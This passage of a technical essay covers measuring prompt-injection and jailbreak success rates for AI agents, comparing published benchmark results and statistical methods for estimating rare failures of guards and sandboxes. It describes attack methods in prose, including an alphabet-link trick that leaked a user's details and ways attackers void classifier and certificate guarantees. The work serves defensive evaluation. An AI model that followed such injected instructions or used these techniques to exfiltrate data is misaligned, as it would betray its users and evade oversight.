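The beta-binomial model removes less than half of the error at a hundred attempts. The remaining error of 22 points suggests that the scenarios differ more sharply than a smooth beta curve fitted at ten attempts allows, with a large group of scenarios in which these attacks almost never work. The fourth column tests this idea with a cruder model, which assumes that attacks never succeed in 39% of scenarios and succeed 7.7% of the time in the others. Like the beta-binomial model, it has two parameters and fits the same two figures, but it comes within about two points of the figure at a hundred attempts.

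This doesn't prove that 39% of the scenarios are immune. If many of the hundred attempts were near-copies, the attacker had fewer than a hundred real chances, and that alone would flatten the curve. For a thousand attempts, the beta-binomial model predicts 99% and the cruder one still predicts 61%, so a fit to small numbers of attempts isn't reliable beyond the range tested.

The fitted parameters also give the correlation within scenarios, which is 1/(a + b + 1). It is about 0.04 for Opus 4.5, and about 0.6 when the same statistical model is applied to Opus 5's browser test without safeguards. A correlation estimated from one test can therefore be far off for another.

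Other published results mostly fall below the simple formula as well:

| Model and test | One attempt | Number of attempts | Formula predicts | Published |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6, computer use | 17.8% | 200 | nearly 100% | 78.6% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, Gray Swan benchmark | 3.1% | 15 | 38% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 5, browser without safeguards | 3.70% | 10 | 31% | 8.5% |
| Claude Opus 5, Gray Swan benchmark | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |
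| Claude Fable 5.1, Gray Swan benchmark | 0.07% | 15 | 1.0% | 1.0% |

The agreement for Fable 5.1 is weak evidence of independence. Only five of 7,124 runs succeeded, and when successes are that rare, most reasonable models predict nearly the same result for 15 attempts.

If scenarios differ and the attacker keeps trying without learning from failures, the formula gives an upper limit on the average chance of success, because variation between scenarios can only lower that average. An attacker who learns from failures can exceed the limit. In tests by Kurakin and colleagues, a team of agents broke 13% of scenarios against Gemini 4 Argon within 150 attempts and 34% within 320. At a constant rate per attempt, it would have broken 26% within 320.

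Testers should therefore measure failures over the number of attempts they care about. For the mail assistant, that means giving an adaptive attacker a hundred messages in each scenario and counting the scenarios in which at least one message works. Each scenario is then one trial, so the exact bound applies without any model of how the attempts relate. Showing a failure rate below 1% takes 299 scenarios with no successful attack, or 29,900 messages.

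### Published rates across developers

Gray Swan's benchmarks are the main source of figures that cover several developers' models. The older one, used to test Opus 4.5 in November 2025, showed attack success rates of up to 92% against rivals such as Gemini 3 Pro and GPT-5.1. By mid-2026 Anthropic had stopped reporting it because Claude models had done so well on it for several releases. The replacement uses attacks from public competitions that worked on several models. These attacks are meant to make agents steal or destroy data, compromise a system or move money.

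| Results published | Model | 1 attempt | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| July 2026, 28 scenarios | Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% |
| | Claude Mythos 5 | | 2.6% |
| | Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% |
| | Muse Spark (Meta) | | 16.5% |
| | GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 3.1% | 20.0% |
| | GPT-5.5 (OpenAI) | | 20.8% |
| | GPT-5.6 Terra (OpenAI) | | 30.4% |
| | GPT-5.6 Luna (OpenAI) | | 43.9% |
| September 2026, 37 scenarios | Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 1.0% |
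| | Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 4.8% |
| | Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 6.5% |
| | Gemini 3.7 Flash (Google) | | 9.2% |

Opus 5 appears twice, and its rate after 15 attempts more than doubled between July and September. The September benchmark had nine more scenarios and 670 more attacks. Anthropic had also begun to require outside testers to leave its blocking classifiers on, and when one of them flagged a request, the older Opus 4.8 answered instead. Fable 5.1's September rate was half of Opus 5's July rate, but when both models were tested on the September benchmark, Fable 5.1's rate was almost four-fifths lower.

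The switch to Opus 4.8 affected 23% of Fable 5.1's runs. Anthropic concludes that this did no harm, because one of 1,653 runs (0.06%) failed when Opus 4.8 answered and four of 5,471 (0.07%) failed when Fable 5.1 did. But the upper bounds on these rates are 0.29% and 0.17%, even if every run is independent, so the true rates could differ considerably.

Comparisons between developers need similar care. Gray Swan tested the Claude models without their specific protections against prompt injection, while the other models ran through public services that may have had such protections. This should favour the other models, yet they did much worse. A rival model can also be at a disadvantage if it was a target in the competitions, because it then faces attacks tailored to it. Anthropic warned in July that Gemini 3.1 Pro's results weren't comparable for this reason, and the September card leaves out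 all such models.

Other developers have published less. VentureBeat compared the system cards available in February 2026 and found that those for GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3 gave no attack success rates by setting or number of attempts. OpenAI's card for GPT-5.5, from April, includes a score for robustness to known attacks on connectors, which link the model to outside services. VentureBeat notes that a higher score is better, unlike with an attack success rate.

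### Published rates by setting

The same model can be easy to hijack in one setting and hard in another. Anthropic's *System Card* (February 2026) for Claude Opus 4.6 covered both cases. VentureBeat reports that no attack succeeded in a coding environment, but when the model operated a screen, 78.6% succeeded within 200 attempts without safeguards and 57.1% with them. Those percentages match 11 and 8 scenarios out of 14, the number in Anthropic's later computer-use tests. The upper bound for 8 of 14 is 79%, so a test this small gives only a rough idea of how well the safeguards worked.

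The next table shows later results for Claude models with extended thinking. The attacker had 200 attempts per scenario in the coding and computer use tests and ten in the browser tests. The safeguards are detectors that scan tool results, plus an action classifier in the browser tests.

| Setting | Model, date of results | Without safeguards | With safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | Opus 4.8, July 2026 | 7.03% of attempts, 23 of 40 scenarios | 2.09%, 15 of 40 |
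| | Opus 5, July 2026 | 0.56%, 13 of 40 | 0.18%, 4 of 40 |
| | Opus 5, September 2026 | 2.68%, 27 of 40 | 0.39%, 11 of 40 |
| | Fable 5.1, September 2026 | 9.26%, 31 of 40 | 2.05%, 18 of 40 |
| Computer use | Opus 4.8, July 2026 | 7.14%, 7 of 14 | 5.11%, 8 of 14 |
| | Opus 5, July 2026 | 0.54%, 1 of 14 | 0.25%, 1 of 14 |
| Browser | Opus 4.8, July 2026 | 31.5%, 81 of 129 | 0.08%, 1 of 129 |
| | Mythos 5, July 2026 | 29.7%, 71 of 129 | 0%, 0 of 129 |
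| | Opus 5, July 2026 | 3.70%, 11 of 129 | 0%, 0 of 129 |
| | Sonnet 5, July 2026 | 0.93%, 9 of 129 | 0%, 0 of 129 |

Safeguards made by far the biggest difference in the browser. Anthropic found that Opus 4.5 in its Chrome extension let through 8.0% of attempts without safeguards, 7.6% with an earlier version of them and 1.4% with an improved version.

Some of the differences in the table are noise. Attackers broke eight of Opus 4.8's computer-use scenarios with safeguards and seven without, and the detectors are unlikely to have helped them. Safeguards can also reduce the success rate per attempt proportionally more than the number of scenarios broken. In the September coding tests, they cut Fable 5.1's rate per attempt by more than three-quarters, but a persistent attacker still broke 18 of the 40 scenarios, down from 31. The scenario counts are the relevant comparison for a company that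 expects such an attacker.

Fable 5.1 had the best results on Gray Swan's benchmark and some of the worst in this table. In the benchmark's coding scenarios, 0.3% of attacks succeeded within 15 attempts, whereas 9.26% of single attempts succeeded in the coding test above. The benchmark replays a fixed collection of attacks, while the coding test uses an attack program that Gray Swan had trained on the same 40 scenarios against earlier Claude models. Some of the successful attacks counted against Fable 5.1 may have been against Opus 4.8, which takes over when a classifier is triggered. The same switch may explain some of Opus 5's rise between July and September.

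The September card also corrects a labelling error in earlier cards. For the Claude 5 models, runs that Gray Swan had labelled "without thinking" had used thinking, because a default setting had changed. Confidence bounds do not account for this kind of error.

Most of these models now have newer versions. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, released on 22 September, reports that the model matched or beat Opus 5 on every prompt injection test, but is more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions. The smaller Haiku 5.5, released in October, resists Gray Swan's attacks less well than Opus 5.5 and Sonnet 5.5, mostly when it operates a screen, according to Pogorelec's *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (2026). Claude Fable 5.2 replaced Fable 5.1 on 9 November (Anthropic, *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude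 Mythos 5.2*, 2026), so the 1.0% in the benchmark table is for a superseded model.

The mail assistant calls tools and doesn't operate a screen, so the tool-use part of the benchmark is its closest match. Fable 5.1's rate there was 0.0% after 15 attempts, compared with 4.1% for operating a screen. The company could use such figures to choose a model, but not as its own h, because the benchmark's attackers weren't trying to leak customer 612's delivery record in a reply to customer 507. They also had only 15 attempts, while an outsider with an email account might have a hundred.

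## Estimating failures too rare or too subtle to count

By the rule of three, showing that a sandbox fails less than once in a million exposures would take about three million trials without a failure. Other failures are hard to recognise one at a time. If a secret makes certain replies only slightly more likely, no single reply looks like a leak. Researchers have proposed several ways to estimate such failures, but each replaces the missing trials with assumptions that an attacker may be able to break.

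### Extrapolating from the riskiest messages

*Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors* (Jones, Tong and colleagues, 2025) estimates the probability that each hostile message works, whereas an ordinary test records only whether it worked. A message that has failed ten times may still have a 1% chance of working on the next run. Much of the risk in a large collection often comes from the few messages with the highest probabilities. The method forecasts how high those probabilities will get as the number of messages grows.

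Testers estimate the probability p for each message in a sample of, say, 1,000. They convert each p to a score, −ln(−ln p), and keep the ten highest. Extreme value theory, the statistics of very large or small values, suggests that these scores rise roughly linearly with the logarithm of the number of messages. The testers fit a line to them and extend it to larger numbers of messages.

As an invented example, suppose the riskiest message in 100 works 0.1% of the time and the riskiest in 1,000 works 1% of the time. The tenfold increase in messages reduces −ln p to two-thirds of its earlier value. If the line stays straight, each further tenfold increase reduces it to two-thirds again.

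| Number of messages | −ln p for the riskiest | Chance that the riskiest works |
|---|---|---|
| 100 (measured) | 6.91 | 0.1% |
| 1,000 (measured) | 4.61 | 1% |
| 10,000 (forecast) | 3.07 | 4.6% |
| 100,000 (forecast) | 2.05 | 13% |

Jones and colleagues tested the method on Claude models from 2024, using requests for instructions to make 19 dangerous chemical and biological substances. From at most 1,000 requests, they forecast the highest probability among up to 90,000 requests. The forecast was within a factor of ten of the true value 72% of the time and too low 34% of the time. The average error was 1.7 orders of magnitude (a factor of about 50), so some forecasts were far off.

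Most of these tests measured the probability of one fixed harmful sentence, which takes little compute but leaves out every other harmful answer. In a smaller test that sampled real answers from Claude 3.5 Haiku, the average error was only a factor of about 1.5.

The method can also forecast the chance that at least one of many messages works. This figure is often more useful for the mail assistant, because thousands of messages that each have a tiny chance of working can add up to a large risk.

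The forecast assumes that future messages come from the same source as the test messages. An attacker who studies the failures and changes technique breaks this assumption. Jones and colleagues limited their misuse tests to attackers who do not adapt. The forecast depends on only ten data points, and the largest extrapolation they tested was a factor of a thousand.

Extrapolation works better for h, the hijack rate, than for e, the rate at which enforcement fails. A model's chance of obeying a message can rise gradually from one wording to the next, but a gateway with a bug usually blocks every forbidden call until somebody finds the input that gets through, so earlier results contain no trend to extrapolate.

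### Estimating rare outputs

Extrapolation needs a probability for each message, and measuring a probability of one in 10,000 by repetition takes tens of thousands of runs. Wu and Hilton (2024) studied an early version of this problem in *Estimating the Probabilities of Rare Outputs in Language Models*. They gave random inputs from a precisely defined source to small models that always choose the most probable token, and estimated how often the models would output a particular rare token.

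One way to estimate how often a model produces a rare token is to search for inputs that produce it and correct for the search. Another is to fit a probability distribution to the model's internal values and extend it to the rare token. In a comparison, both did better than plain random sampling, and the search did best.

Parulekar and Liu (2026), in *Estimating Rare Events in Language Models with Proper Evaluation*, returned to the same test with probabilities between one in 100,000 and one in a billion. The true values came from running about four billion random inputs. For the rarest tokens, the search methods often found no input that produced the token and returned an estimate of zero. The best older method based on internal values tended to overestimate. Their own method was closer to the truth on average, but its errors varied more from token to token. They conclude that the best choice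 depends on how harmful each kind of error is. A sandbox auditor would probably prefer overestimates.

More recent methods keep the input fixed and estimate how often a model's random sampling leads to a bad answer. In *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions*, Angell, Singhal and colleagues (2026) tested Llama-3.1-8B, a small open model, on 313 harmful requests. The model gave a harmful answer to 1.6% of the requests when it always chose the most probable token. When they sampled 10,000 answers to each request, it gave at least one harmful answer to 74% of the requests.

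Their method is importance sampling. They make a copy of the model that misbehaves more often by adding a fixed pattern to its internal activity, then sample answers from the copy. Each bad answer counts in proportion to how likely the original model was to write it:

estimate = (1/k) × Σ h(xᵢ) × p(xᵢ)/q(xᵢ).

Here k is the number of answers, h(xᵢ) is 1 if answer xᵢ is harmful and 0 otherwise, and p and q are the probabilities that the original and the copy would write that answer. Suppose the copy gives 50 harmful answers in 500 runs, and it was 1,000 times as likely as the original to write each one. Each then counts as a thousandth of a failure, so the original's estimated failure rate is 50 × 0.001 ÷ 500, or one in 10,000.

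In tests on open models, the method's estimates from 500 to 1,000 answers matched direct counts over 10,000 answers. The method needs access to the model's weights. An LLM judge decides which answers are harmful, so the judge's mistakes carry over into the estimate.

The copy also has to fail in the same ways as the original. If it rarely produces one of the original's typical failures, most estimates will be too low, but occasionally one such answer will appear with an enormous importance weight and make the estimate far too high. In *Rare Event Estimation via Iterative Unalignment*, Yang, Mittal and colleagues (2026) try to prevent this by adjusting the copy's parameters step by step and holding back when the importance weights become unstable. For events with probabilities between one in ten million and one in a billion, the method was on average more than 800 times as efficient as direct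 sampling. The researchers used simple events, such as the appearance of certain tokens, so that they could calculate the true probabilities. Even so, for events rarer than one in ten million, 95% of estimates on GPT-2 were typically within a factor of about 16 of the true probability.

*Weighted Ensemble Sampling for Rare-Event Estimation in Language Models* (Liu, Didier and colleagues, 2026) describes a method that does not use the altered copy. The method starts many answers at once, pauses them partway, and uses the model's internal activity to group those with similar chances of going wrong. It then makes extra copies of answers in small groups that seem more likely to go wrong and drops some from large groups that seem harmless.

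For example, suppose one of 100 unfinished answers looks dangerous. The program might continue with 50 copies of it, each carrying a weight of 0.02%, and 50 of the others, each carrying 1.98%. The dangerous group still carries 1% of the total weight. If five of the dangerous copies and none of the other answers end in a leak, the estimated leak rate is 5 × 0.02%, or 0.1%. The estimate is correct on average however the program forms the groups, but poor groups make it less precise.

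These methods need the model's weights or internal activity, so the model's developer could apply them, but a company that uses the model over the internet can't. The published tests also cover single pieces of generated text, whereas an agent's run includes tool results and replies from other people. Angell and colleagues suggest simulating the other party and multiplying the probability ratios from each turn, but the product is likely to vary more as the run gets longer.

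An attacker can send a different message. When Angell and colleagues had a model reword harmful requests without trying to make them more effective, the probability of a harmful answer often changed by several orders of magnitude. For one request to Phi-4, it rose from less than one in a million to 19%. These methods are therefore more useful for estimating the probabilities that go into an extrapolation. Angell and colleagues used them this way, and their estimates for 30% of 7,725 reworded requests forecast the worst cases in the other 70% well.

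### Certificates from randomised smoothing

Randomised smoothing runs a model on many randomly altered copies of an input and returns the most common output. A small change to the input affects only some of the copies, so it can't overturn a large enough majority. Researchers developed the technique for image classifiers, where it gives a proof that covers every sufficiently small change, including changes nobody has tried.

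SmoothLLM applies the idea to jailbreaks by changing random characters in a prompt. Its original certificate assumed that an attack always fails once at least k characters of it have changed. Kumarappan and Mehrotra (2025), in *Towards Realistic Guarantees*, found that success rates fall gradually instead, and never quite reached zero in their tests. Their certificate assumes only that the attack succeeds with probability at most ε after k or more changes. If so, the chance that one altered copy gets a safe answer is at least

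(1 − ε) × P(at least k of the changed characters fall inside the attack).

In the paper's worked case, a prompt has 240 characters, 100 of which belong to an attack string, and SmoothLLM changes 24 at random. With k = 6 and ε = 5%, at least six changes fall inside the attack string 97.8% of the time, so each copy has at least a 92.9% chance of being safe. A vote among ten copies then gives a safe result more than 99.9% of the time, well above the 95% target.

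The weak point is ε, which must be the value for the particular attack, but Kumarappan and Mehrotra estimate it as an average over many attacks. If one attack in 20 survives every alteration and the others survive none, the average is also 5%, but the vote fails against that one attack in 20 no matter how many copies it uses.

The worked case covers attack strings produced by GCG, a search program, against the 7-billion-parameter Llama 2. These strings are fragile, while prompts from PAIR, in which a model rewrites a request in ordinary language, withstand alterations better and need a larger k. The certificate assumes that the attacker does not adapt to the alterations, but an attacker could repeat an instruction several times in plain words so that random typing errors don't destroy it. On the mail assistant, the alterations could also damage a genuine customer's order number.

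Cheng, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment*, hide random tokens instead of changing characters. They also train the model to judge a request from the tokens that remain. Their certificate is supposed to cover an attacker who replaces up to R tokens of the user's text in any way. Let c be the share of copies in which all of the attacker's tokens are hidden, and let the margin be the winning side's share of the vote minus the losing side's. The theorem promises safety if

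margin > 1 − 2c,

but the proof arrives at

margin > 2 − 2c.

In the recommended setting, each copy keeps 70% of the tokens, so a single replaced token appears in 70% of the copies. In the worst case, all of those copies vote as the attacker wants and the attacker wins. A margin above 40% would satisfy the theorem's condition, but the proof's condition requires one above 140%, which is impossible. The paper reports average certificates of about 14 or 15 tokens at this setting, but its proof doesn't support a certificate for even one.

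The proof's condition requires the method to hide more than half of the tokens to cover one replacement, and about 90% to cover six. When it hid 90%, the model's score on MMLU, a test of general knowledge, fell to 34.2%, half its score in the recommended setting. The defence cut the success rate of GCG attacks from 84.2% to 1.2% in tests, but this result doesn't guarantee protection against new attacks.

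Even a correct certificate would guarantee only that the vote stays the same for all inputs close to the tested one. The vote itself may be wrong, and an attacker can write a new hostile email that is not close to any message the company has certified.

### Calibrated guards

A company that uses a model to block attacks will probably try several prompts for it and keep the one that scores best. That score is likely to flatter the winner, because some prompts do well on a particular test set by luck. Jawad, Landeau and colleagues (2026), in *Risk-Certified Prompt Optimization for LLM-as-a-Judge Guardrails*, correct for this with an (α, ε, δ) guarantee. With a probability of at least 1 − δ, two things are true:

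- every prompt the method certifies misses at most a share α of attacks;
- the chosen prompt lets through nearly as many harmless inputs as the best certified one, with a gap of at most ε.

The simpler of their two procedures writes 20 prompts using one set of examples and tests them on another. It computes a Clopper–Pearson upper bound on each prompt's miss rate, using a stricter confidence level because it tests 20 prompts at once. It keeps the prompts whose bound is below α and picks the one that blocks the fewest harmless inputs. The other procedure writes new prompts in response to earlier results, and limits the information it takes from the test set so that the guarantee still holds.

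With δ set to 10%, every certified prompt stayed within its target on fresh examples. The table shows results for the second procedure, with GPT-4o-mini judging whether outside text contains hidden instructions.

| Maximum miss rate (α) | Attacks missed | Harmless inputs allowed |
|---|---|---|
| 10% | 2% | 58% |
| 20% | 11% | 86% |
| 30% | 20% | 86% |

An uncorrected prompt missed 60% of the attacks and allowed 90% of the harmless inputs. In four of 12 settings, the simpler procedure could not certify any prompt.

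These targets are far above the rates of rare failures, and stricter targets need many more examples. If the whole 10% is allotted to the limit on misses, certifying one of 20 prompts at α = 10% requires at least 51 attacks with no misses. At α = 0.1%, it requires about 5,300.

The guarantee holds only when future inputs resemble random draws from the same source as the test examples. A new kind of attack, a different mix of users or an update to the judge's model can void it. It also doesn't cover an attacker who tries many versions of a message. Jawad and colleagues tested that case separately. When the attacker had 100 attempts, the prompt certified at 10% missed at most 7% of attacks, while two ordinary optimised prompts missed 80%. The certified prompt also blocked 42% of harmless inputs, which may explain much of its resistance.

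The company could limit m, the action classifier's miss rate, by using the method on replies from a hijacked mail assistant. It would have to repeat the calibration whenever the attacks changed.

### Measuring influence by swapping inputs

Information-flow labels can forbid a flow of data, but they don't measure how much a model's output depends on something it has read. Noninterference offers a way to define that dependence. In its original form, one group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second can see. For the mail assistant, nothing that customer 507 sees should depend on customer 612's delivery record.

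Di Pierro, Hankin and Wiklicky (2004), in *Approximate Non-interference*, point out that real systems hardly ever meet this standard, and replace it with a limit on the size of the effect. Adapted to the mail assistant, the rule compares two inputs, x and x′, that are identical except for the protected part. The assistant meets the limit ε if, for every such pair and every outcome o that the observer could see,

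|P(o given x) − P(o given x′)| ≤ ε.

One of their examples shows why the probabilities matter. A program holds a secret bit, 0 or 1. It prints the secret half the time and a random bit the other half. Both outputs are possible whatever the secret is, so a list of possible outputs reveals nothing. But the program prints 1 in 75% of runs if the secret is 1 and in 25% if it is 0, a difference of 50 percentage points. An observer can soon infer the secret by running the program several times. Di Pierro and colleagues relate ε to the number of runs needed to tell the two cases apart.

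*AgentSecBench* (2026) adapts noninterference to measure how much hostile text influences an agent. It treats the system's instructions and the user's request as trusted inputs and retrieved material as untrusted. The testers keep the trusted inputs fixed, swap the untrusted text, and compare how often a chosen outcome occurs.

For the mail assistant, the outcome might be an outside send, meaning an attempt to send a message to a third address. Suppose the gateway is set to allow every call, and outside sends occur in 0.2% of 1,000 runs with a harmless message and 0.9% of 1,000 runs with a hostile one. Ignoring sampling error, the estimated influence is at least 0.7 percentage points. This is a lower bound because ε is the largest difference over all outcomes and all pairs of messages, and the test measured one outcome for one pair. The hostile message might have a much larger effect on another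 outcome, such as the delivery date in the reply.

The sampling error is large because the estimate rests on two sends against nine. If the hostile text had no effect, a split at least that uneven would still occur in about one in 15 tests. A 95% interval for the difference runs from about zero to 1.5 percentage points. With 10,000 runs of each kind and the same rates, it would run from about 0.5 to 0.9.

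A small influence per message can also add up over many messages. If the runs were independent, 18% of batches of 100 harmless messages and 60% of batches of 100 hostile ones would include at least one outside send, a difference of about 41 percentage points.

The two messages should differ only in the part under test. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) notes that an agent's decision should depend on the parts of outside data that matter to the task. If the harmless message asked about a different order, the assistant would rightly behave differently, and the test would count that as influence. Testers can avoid this by keeping the customer's question and replacing only the hidden instruction with harmless text of the same length.

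*SwarmSafe-Delta* (2026) shows how to build such a comparison for messages between agents. It freezes a run just before one agent receives a message, then continues it with the original message, with no message, and with neutral text of the same word count. For a smaller set of runs, it also repeats the original prompt exactly, which shows how much the results vary by chance.

Irrelevant details of the computer's state can also change the result. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* (2026) describes running the same case from Agent Security Bench twice, changing only the hash seed, a number that can affect the order in which a program handles data. The verdict should be the same both times, but the paper finds that in current practice it is not always. Testers can hold such details constant where possible, or choose them at random for both kinds of run and average the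 results.

To test for leaked secrets, the company would swap the secret instead of the message. It could run the same hostile email from customer 507 with two different delivery dates in customer 612's record and compare everything customer 507 can see. A difference would reveal a leak even if no reply stated the date. The comparison must include indirect signals such as response times and network requests, since a test that recorded only replies would have missed the leak through `ping` in Claude Code.

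A swap test requires no access to the model's weights and no theory of how the attack works. But a result near zero applies only to the messages, secrets and outcomes tested, and an attacker can use others.

| Method | What it estimates | Main assumptions | How an attacker can void it | Suitable use |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tail extrapolation | The highest or combined risk in a much larger set of messages | Future messages come from the same source, and the trend continues | Learning from failures and changing technique | Forecasting hijacks from high-volume, non-adaptive attacks |
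| Rare-output estimation | The chance of a rare bad output, for a fixed input or a defined source of inputs | Access to the model's internals, and sampling that reaches all the important failures | Rewording the message | Measuring known high-risk messages, or supplying probabilities for extrapolation |
| Smoothing certificate | Whether a vote resists limited changes to an input | A correct proof, and an ε that holds for each attack if the certificate uses one | Making larger changes, or writing text that survives the alterations | Defending against fragile attack strings |
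| Calibrated guard | An upper limit on the share of attacks a guard misses | Future inputs resemble random draws from the calibration source | Using new kinds of attack or many attempts | Choosing a guard's prompt for stable, familiar traffic |
| Input swapping | A lower limit on the influence of a text or secret, before sampling error | The two inputs differ only in the part under test, and other conditions match | Using a message or outcome outside the test | Finding subtle leaks and comparing versions of a sandbox |

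## Deciding whether the sandbox is good enough and keeping the estimate valid

A breach rate of 0.04% may be excellent for an assistant that recommends restaurants and unacceptable for one that makes payments. The company with the mail assistant needs to set a limit for its own breach rate based on how much harm one breach does and how many hostile messages arrive.

### Setting the limit

If the company can put a price on a breach, the highest acceptable rate per exposure is

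acceptable rate = tolerated loss per year ÷ (exposures per year × harm of one breach).

Suppose 1,000 hostile messages arrive each year, a leak of one customer's record costs about $20,000, and the company will accept an average loss of $2,000 a year. The limit on the breach rate is then 0.01%, or one breach in 10,000 exposures. A false delivery date might cost only $50, which gives a limit of 4% for the same accepted loss, so each harmful effect needs its own limit.

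Some harms are hard to price. The company can instead choose q, the highest chance of any breach in a year that it will accept. With n exposures a year, the limit is approximately

−ln(1 − q) ÷ n.

Butler and Finelli (1993), in *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software*, used this conversion to turn a safety target for a whole flight into one for each input to the flight software. If the company accepts a 10% chance of a breach, its limit is 0.0105% per exposure, or about one in 9,500.

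The next table applies the breach rates from the earlier invented examples to 1,000 exposures. The upper bounds come from tests of the complete system and are calculated assuming that the exposures are independent.

| Permissions and figure used | Breach rate | Breaches per year | Chance of at least one |
|---|---|---|---|
| Starting permissions, estimate | 0.40% | 4.0 | 98% |
| Starting permissions, upper bound after 8 breaches in 2,000 exposures | 0.72% | 7.2 | 99.9% |
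| Narrower permissions, estimate | 0.042% | 0.42 | 34% |
| Narrower permissions, upper bound after no breaches in 2,000 exposures | 0.15% | 1.5 | 78% |

The starting permissions fail by any reasonable standard. The narrower ones also miss the 10% limit, but a company willing to accept a one-in-three chance might approve them based on the estimate. It would reject them based on the upper bound, because a clean test of 2,000 exposures can't rule out a rate more than three times the estimate. Deciding on the bound is safer because a small test then makes the sandbox harder to approve, not easier.

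The average number of breaches doesn't depend on whether the exposures are independent, but the chance of at least one does. An attacker who finds a wording that works will use it again, so an average of four breaches a year could mean nine years with none and 40 in the tenth. The attacker also decides how many messages to send. The company can limit this by pausing automatic replies to a sender after the monitor refuses a call.

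A higher breach rate is acceptable if each breach does less harm. In *GoEx*, Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) propose that agents should be able to undo their actions where possible, for example by keeping a copy of an email before deleting it. For actions that can't be undone, such as sending an email that can no longer be recalled, they propose limiting the damage instead, perhaps by letting the agent read mail but not send it. The mail assistant could hold each reply for an hour so that an employee can cancel it, though this helps only if someone notices the problem in time.

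### Does a barrier that sometimes fails count as a boundary?

Willison thinks a detector that catches 99% of attacks is useless as a defence, because "in application security 99% is a failing grade". An attacker's job is to find the other 1%. Willison (2025), *My Lethal Trifecta talk at the Bay Area AI Security Meetup*, compares this with SQL injection and argues that if database defences had worked only 99% of the time, thieves would have emptied our bank accounts decades ago.

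Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, recommends changing what the agent can do. He warns against combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. An attacker needs all three to steal data, so removing any one prevents the theft. The mail assistant has all three. The rule covers only data theft, so an agent that can delete files needs other limits as well.

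David C, writing for the National Cyber Security Centre, also starts from SQL injection but treats prompt injection as a residual risk, one that remains after every available defence. No product can remove it, so a system's owners have to manage it through design, construction and operation. If they can't tolerate the remaining risk, the task may not be a good use for an LLM. On this view, owners can use a barrier with a known failure rate if they can tolerate its failures.

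David C and Willison disagree less than their language suggests. David C prioritizes ordinary code over attempts to keep hostile text away from the model, and warns against any product whose seller claims it can stop prompt injection. Willison doesn't reject every system with some remaining risk. In *163 posts tagged “prompt-injection”*, he describes a public challenge in which Fernando Irarrázaval invited people to extract a secret from his assistant by email. The assistant ran on Claude Opus 4.6 with written instructions not to reveal secrets, and none of about 6,000 attempts succeeded. Willison was impressed, but still advised against using such a system where an attack could do irreversible damage.

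Even if those 6,000 attempts were independent and typical of real attacks, the upper bound on the leak rate would be 0.05%. With 1,000 hostile messages a year, the annual chance of at least one leak could be as high as 39%. Whether that risk is acceptable depends on how much harm leaking the secret would do.

Calling something a "boundary" still matters because designers rely on whatever is behind it. Christodorescu and colleagues hold that the trusted computing base should contain nothing an attacker can affect. This excludes a detector, however well it scores, because its verdict depends on text the attacker chose.

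Ordinary code fails too, but developers can usually repair it more completely than a trained detector. A detector trained on a message that got past it may still miss a different wording. Anthropic's Claude chat had a tool that opened only web addresses that the user had typed, a search had returned, or pages it had already opened contained. Ayush Paul found that links on opened pages could be used to leak data. He built a site with a link for each letter of the alphabet and told the model to spell out the user's name by following them. The model revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on pages it had opened, and no rewording of Paul's message can reopen that route.

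It therefore seems best to reserve "boundary" for limits that don't depend on a model's judgement, and to treat detectors as lowering the hijack rate. OpenAI offers both kinds of protection. Its Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT limits outgoing network requests, so an injected instruction has fewer ways to send data out. Dane Stuckey, the company's chief information security officer, said the mode is for people at elevated risk, who should find the loss of features worthwhile. Other users keep the features and accept more risk, which is consistent with a limit based on harm.

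### When to stop testing and remove a permission

Butler and Finelli, who worked at NASA, calculated how long it would take to test flight software that is allowed a one-in-a-billion chance of failing during a ten-hour flight. Software at that limit fails about once every ten billion hours, so testers running one copy would wait more than 1.1 million years, on average, to see a failure. With 10,000 copies, they would wait 114 years.

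Fixing bugs and extrapolating from the improvement doesn't help much. For one small program, a model that extrapolates this way predicted that testers would have to remove 23 bugs to reach the target, and that the last of them would take about 340,000 years to appear.

The mail assistant is easier to test than an aircraft because it handles few hostile inputs and testers can run them quickly. Butler and Finelli point out that if software received one input a month and a test took a tenth of a second, testing to the same flight target would take only 16 days. For the mail assistant, three million trials would give an upper bound of one in a million if every trial were clean and independent. At ten seconds each, running a hundred at a time, they would take three and a half days.

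The bound would be of little use, though. *Validation of Ultrahigh Dependability for Software-Based Systems* (Littlewood and Strigini, 1993) argued that every kind of evidence about software runs into limits as the target gets stricter. Their retrospective, *Validation of ultra-high dependability…* (2011), notes that faster computers have made very long tests possible, but that other doubts then dominate, such as whether the test program runs and judges each case correctly. Testers running attacks must also ask whether those attacks resemble what a real attacker will do.

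Butler and Finelli show why testing also can't justify multiplying the failure rates of two layers to get a tiny combined rate. Suppose each of two programs fails once in 100,000 hours. If they failed independently, they would fail together about once in ten billion hours. But if they actually failed together once in ten million hours, a century of testing would probably still reveal no joint failure.

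The point beyond which testing is hopeless depends on the system, the available evidence and the budget. Littlewood and Strigini never set a fixed number for it, although other writers have credited them with one. For the mail assistant, showing a rate below 0.0105% takes about 28,400 clean exposures. If each has to be a different scenario to count as independent, few companies could produce that many. At that point it makes more sense to remove a permission than to continue testing.

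Butler and Finelli saw only two options for flight software, weakening the requirement or going without measurement, and liked neither. An LLM component can often do without some of its permissions, whereas flight software has to control the aircraft. *Agentic AI and Security* (2025), a guide for software developers, disagrees with Willison about which to remove first. It considers untrusted content the simplest to avoid and advises against letting an LLM read email, which would leave the mail assistant with nothing to do. Willison finds outgoing communication the easiest to restrict, and this suits the company better.

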